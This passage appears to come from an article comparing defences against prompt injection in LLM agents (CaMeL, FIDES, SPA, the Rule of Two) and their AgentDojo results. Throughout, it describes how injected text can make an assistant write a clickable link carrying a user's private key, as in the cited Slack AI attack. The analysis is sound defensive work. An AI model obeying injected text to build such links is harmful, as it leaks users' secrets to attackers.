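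The quarantined model may still be able to put a malicious link in the answer. Suppose the plan is to search the user's messages, have the quarantined model answer the question from the results, and show the answer. If the results include both a private key and the attacker's message, the quarantined model could write the link without changing the plan. The interpreter's records would show that the answer came partly from an outsider, but that helps only if something checks them before the answer appears. Tallam and Miller (2025), in *Operationalizing CaMeL*, write that CaMeL "does not inspect what the agent ultimately outputs". They propose scanning answers for suspicious addresses and other signs of manipulation. Checking the interpreter's records would be more dependable, since it wouldn't require recognising an attack by its appearance.

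Costa and colleagues' FIDES system stores untrusted tool results in variables. The planning model receives a variable's name and can pass it to a tool without reading the contents. If the plan depends on the contents, the planning model can query a separate quarantined model and restrict the reply to a type such as yes or no. A yes-or-no reply limits the influence of untrusted text on the plan to one bit.

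FIDES applies a policy to sending emails that is much like the link rule. It allows an email if every recipient is permitted to read the contents, or if no untrusted content influenced the decision to send it. Costa and colleagues describe the second case as a form of robust declassification.

When the agent sends an email or message, FIDES treats an untrusted link in the text as a reason to block it, to prevent data theft through web requests. FIDES doesn't apply this policy to the agent's answers, because it treats a response to the user as having no consequences. But the same link in an answer could leak data if the user clicked it.

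The design would make this gap fairly easy to close. The final answer already has labels, and Costa and colleagues note that the system can check it against policies if an application needs that. In one of their examples, the answer refers to a summary of hotel reviews by its variable name, and the summary stays hidden. If the application later replaced the name with the summary, it could check any links in the summary before showing them.

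### What the benchmark results cover

Both systems have results on AgentDojo, a set of simulated office, travel, banking and Slack tasks, some with planted attacks. Costa and colleagues ran 97 ordinary tasks and combined them with 36 attack goals. With OpenAI's GPT-4o as the model, 152 attacks succeeded against a basic agent and none succeeded against FIDES with its checks on.

The next table shows the percentage of ordinary tasks that each agent completed when there was no attack. The last column is the plain average of the four environments.

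| Agent | Office | Travel | Banking | Slack | Average |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic, no checks, GPT-4o | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 | 84.3 |
| Basic, with label checks, GPT-4o | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 | 41.9 |
| FIDES, with label checks, GPT-4o | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 | 50.0 |
| FIDES, with label checks, o1 | 64.5 | 68.0 | 56.2 | 54.3 | 60.8 |

Adding label checks to the basic agent halved its average score, because a single untrusted email restricted what the agent could do afterwards. Hiding untrusted text in variables recovered some of the loss, and using the stronger o1 model recovered more. Both models are now old. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) predicts that the drawbacks of CaMeL's approach will shrink as models get better at planning and writing code.

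The perfect security score has two limits. Costa and colleagues marked a data field as untrusted if any attack in the benchmark used it, whereas a real developer wouldn't know in advance where attacks would appear. They also didn't count attacks that changed only the text of an answer, such as one that made the agent praise a particular place to visit. An answer with a stolen key in a link would also reach the user as text, so the score doesn't show that FIDES would stop data theft through links that users click.

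In one failed task, the user wanted a password-reset link from their mailbox, but the agent couldn't tell which senders to trust and didn't return the right link. Costa and colleagues suggest that a planner that uses the labels could return only links from trusted senders.

Accounts of CaMeL's usefulness differ. Tallam and Miller report that it completed 67% of AgentDojo tasks. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) describes it as performing about as well as an unprotected agent while stopping nearly all attacks. Kolluri and colleagues cite losses in usefulness of up to 30% for systems of this type, including CaMeL.

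They also think the usual comparison is unfair to these systems, because it counts a task as failed if the agent needs a person's approval, while the unprotected agent may do anything without asking. They therefore count how many approvals an agent needs. Prudentia, which adds knowledge of the labels and policies to FIDES, reduced that number by a factor of up to 1.9. With no approvals allowed, it completed up to 9% more tasks than FIDES. A similar count for links would show how many dialogs a user has to answer in a normal week.

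### Newer systems that control output

Some systems published in 2026 restrict what they show the user. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) describes an agent that writes its whole plan before using any tools. Showing something to the user is a step in the plan, and the software checks whether private information may be shown.

SPA also tracks how private data affects the choice of steps, whereas the FIDES guarantee does not cover leaks through those choices. In attacks that use prepared public addresses, SPA's labels could therefore record that private data determined which link appeared. With its label checks on, SPA reduced attack success on AgentDojo to zero, but the share of ordinary tasks it completed fell from 53% to 29%.

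To protect a link, a check on output has to treat the link's address as a separate output, read by the owner of the destination server. A policy that considered only the person at the screen would have let the answer through in the Slack AI attack, because the developer was allowed to see the key.

*Environment Steering* (2026) also applies a policy to the model's response. In its healthcare tests, a model writes a policy for each task to keep unnecessary private details out of the answer. This would help if the user's question had nothing to do with the key, but less so in the Slack AI case, where the developer had asked for it.

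*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026) describes a system with two output channels, so that when the agent prints a secret, the user's terminal shows the real text but the cloud model receives only asterisks. The agent's code can transform the secret only with functions that have no side effects, so it can't send the secret anywhere. But appending the secret to a partial web address also has no side effects. If the terminal made the resulting address clickable, the user could leak the secret by clicking it.

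### The lethal trifecta and the Rule of Two

A developer can also avoid the problem without labelling individual values. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, Willison (2025) advises people never to combine access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate with the outside. He counts a link for the user to click as a way to send data out.

Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns this idea into a design rule. Within one session, an agent may have at most two of these three properties: it processes untrusted input, it has access to private data or sensitive systems, or it can change things or communicate externally. An agent that needs all three must have supervision, such as human approval. Meta's post doesn't discuss clickable links.

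A clickable link should count as external communication whenever untrusted text can influence its address or the choice of link, even though the user's browser sends the request and the agent doesn't. If links didn't count, an assistant that reads private and public messages and can only write answers would satisfy the rule. PromptArmor's attack on Slack AI required only those abilities.

Clicking a link is a poor substitute for the human approval that Meta's rule requires. Meta warns that even a design that follows the rule can fail if a user blindly confirms a warning.

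If links count as a way to send data out, a web search assistant with no private data can still show them freely, and so can a company assistant that reads only trusted documents. An assistant for a mailbox that receives email from strangers can't show links that the model has written. Meta's example of a travel assistant suggests a less drastic limit. That assistant has the user's private information and reads the web, so it may visit only addresses returned by trusted sources, not addresses it has constructed. A developer could apply the same limit to the links an assistant displays, although the choice among fixed addresses can still reveal a little private information.

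The permissions can also change during a session. Meta describes an agent that first searches the web and then permanently loses outside communication when it opens internal systems. A chat application could similarly show clickable links until private data enters the context, then remove links from all later answers. The earlier links could safely stay on the screen because the model wrote them before it had the private data.

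This is much easier to build than label tracking, because the software only needs to record which sources the assistant has opened. But after asking about an email, a user would lose even harmless map links for the rest of the session, unless ordinary code built them.
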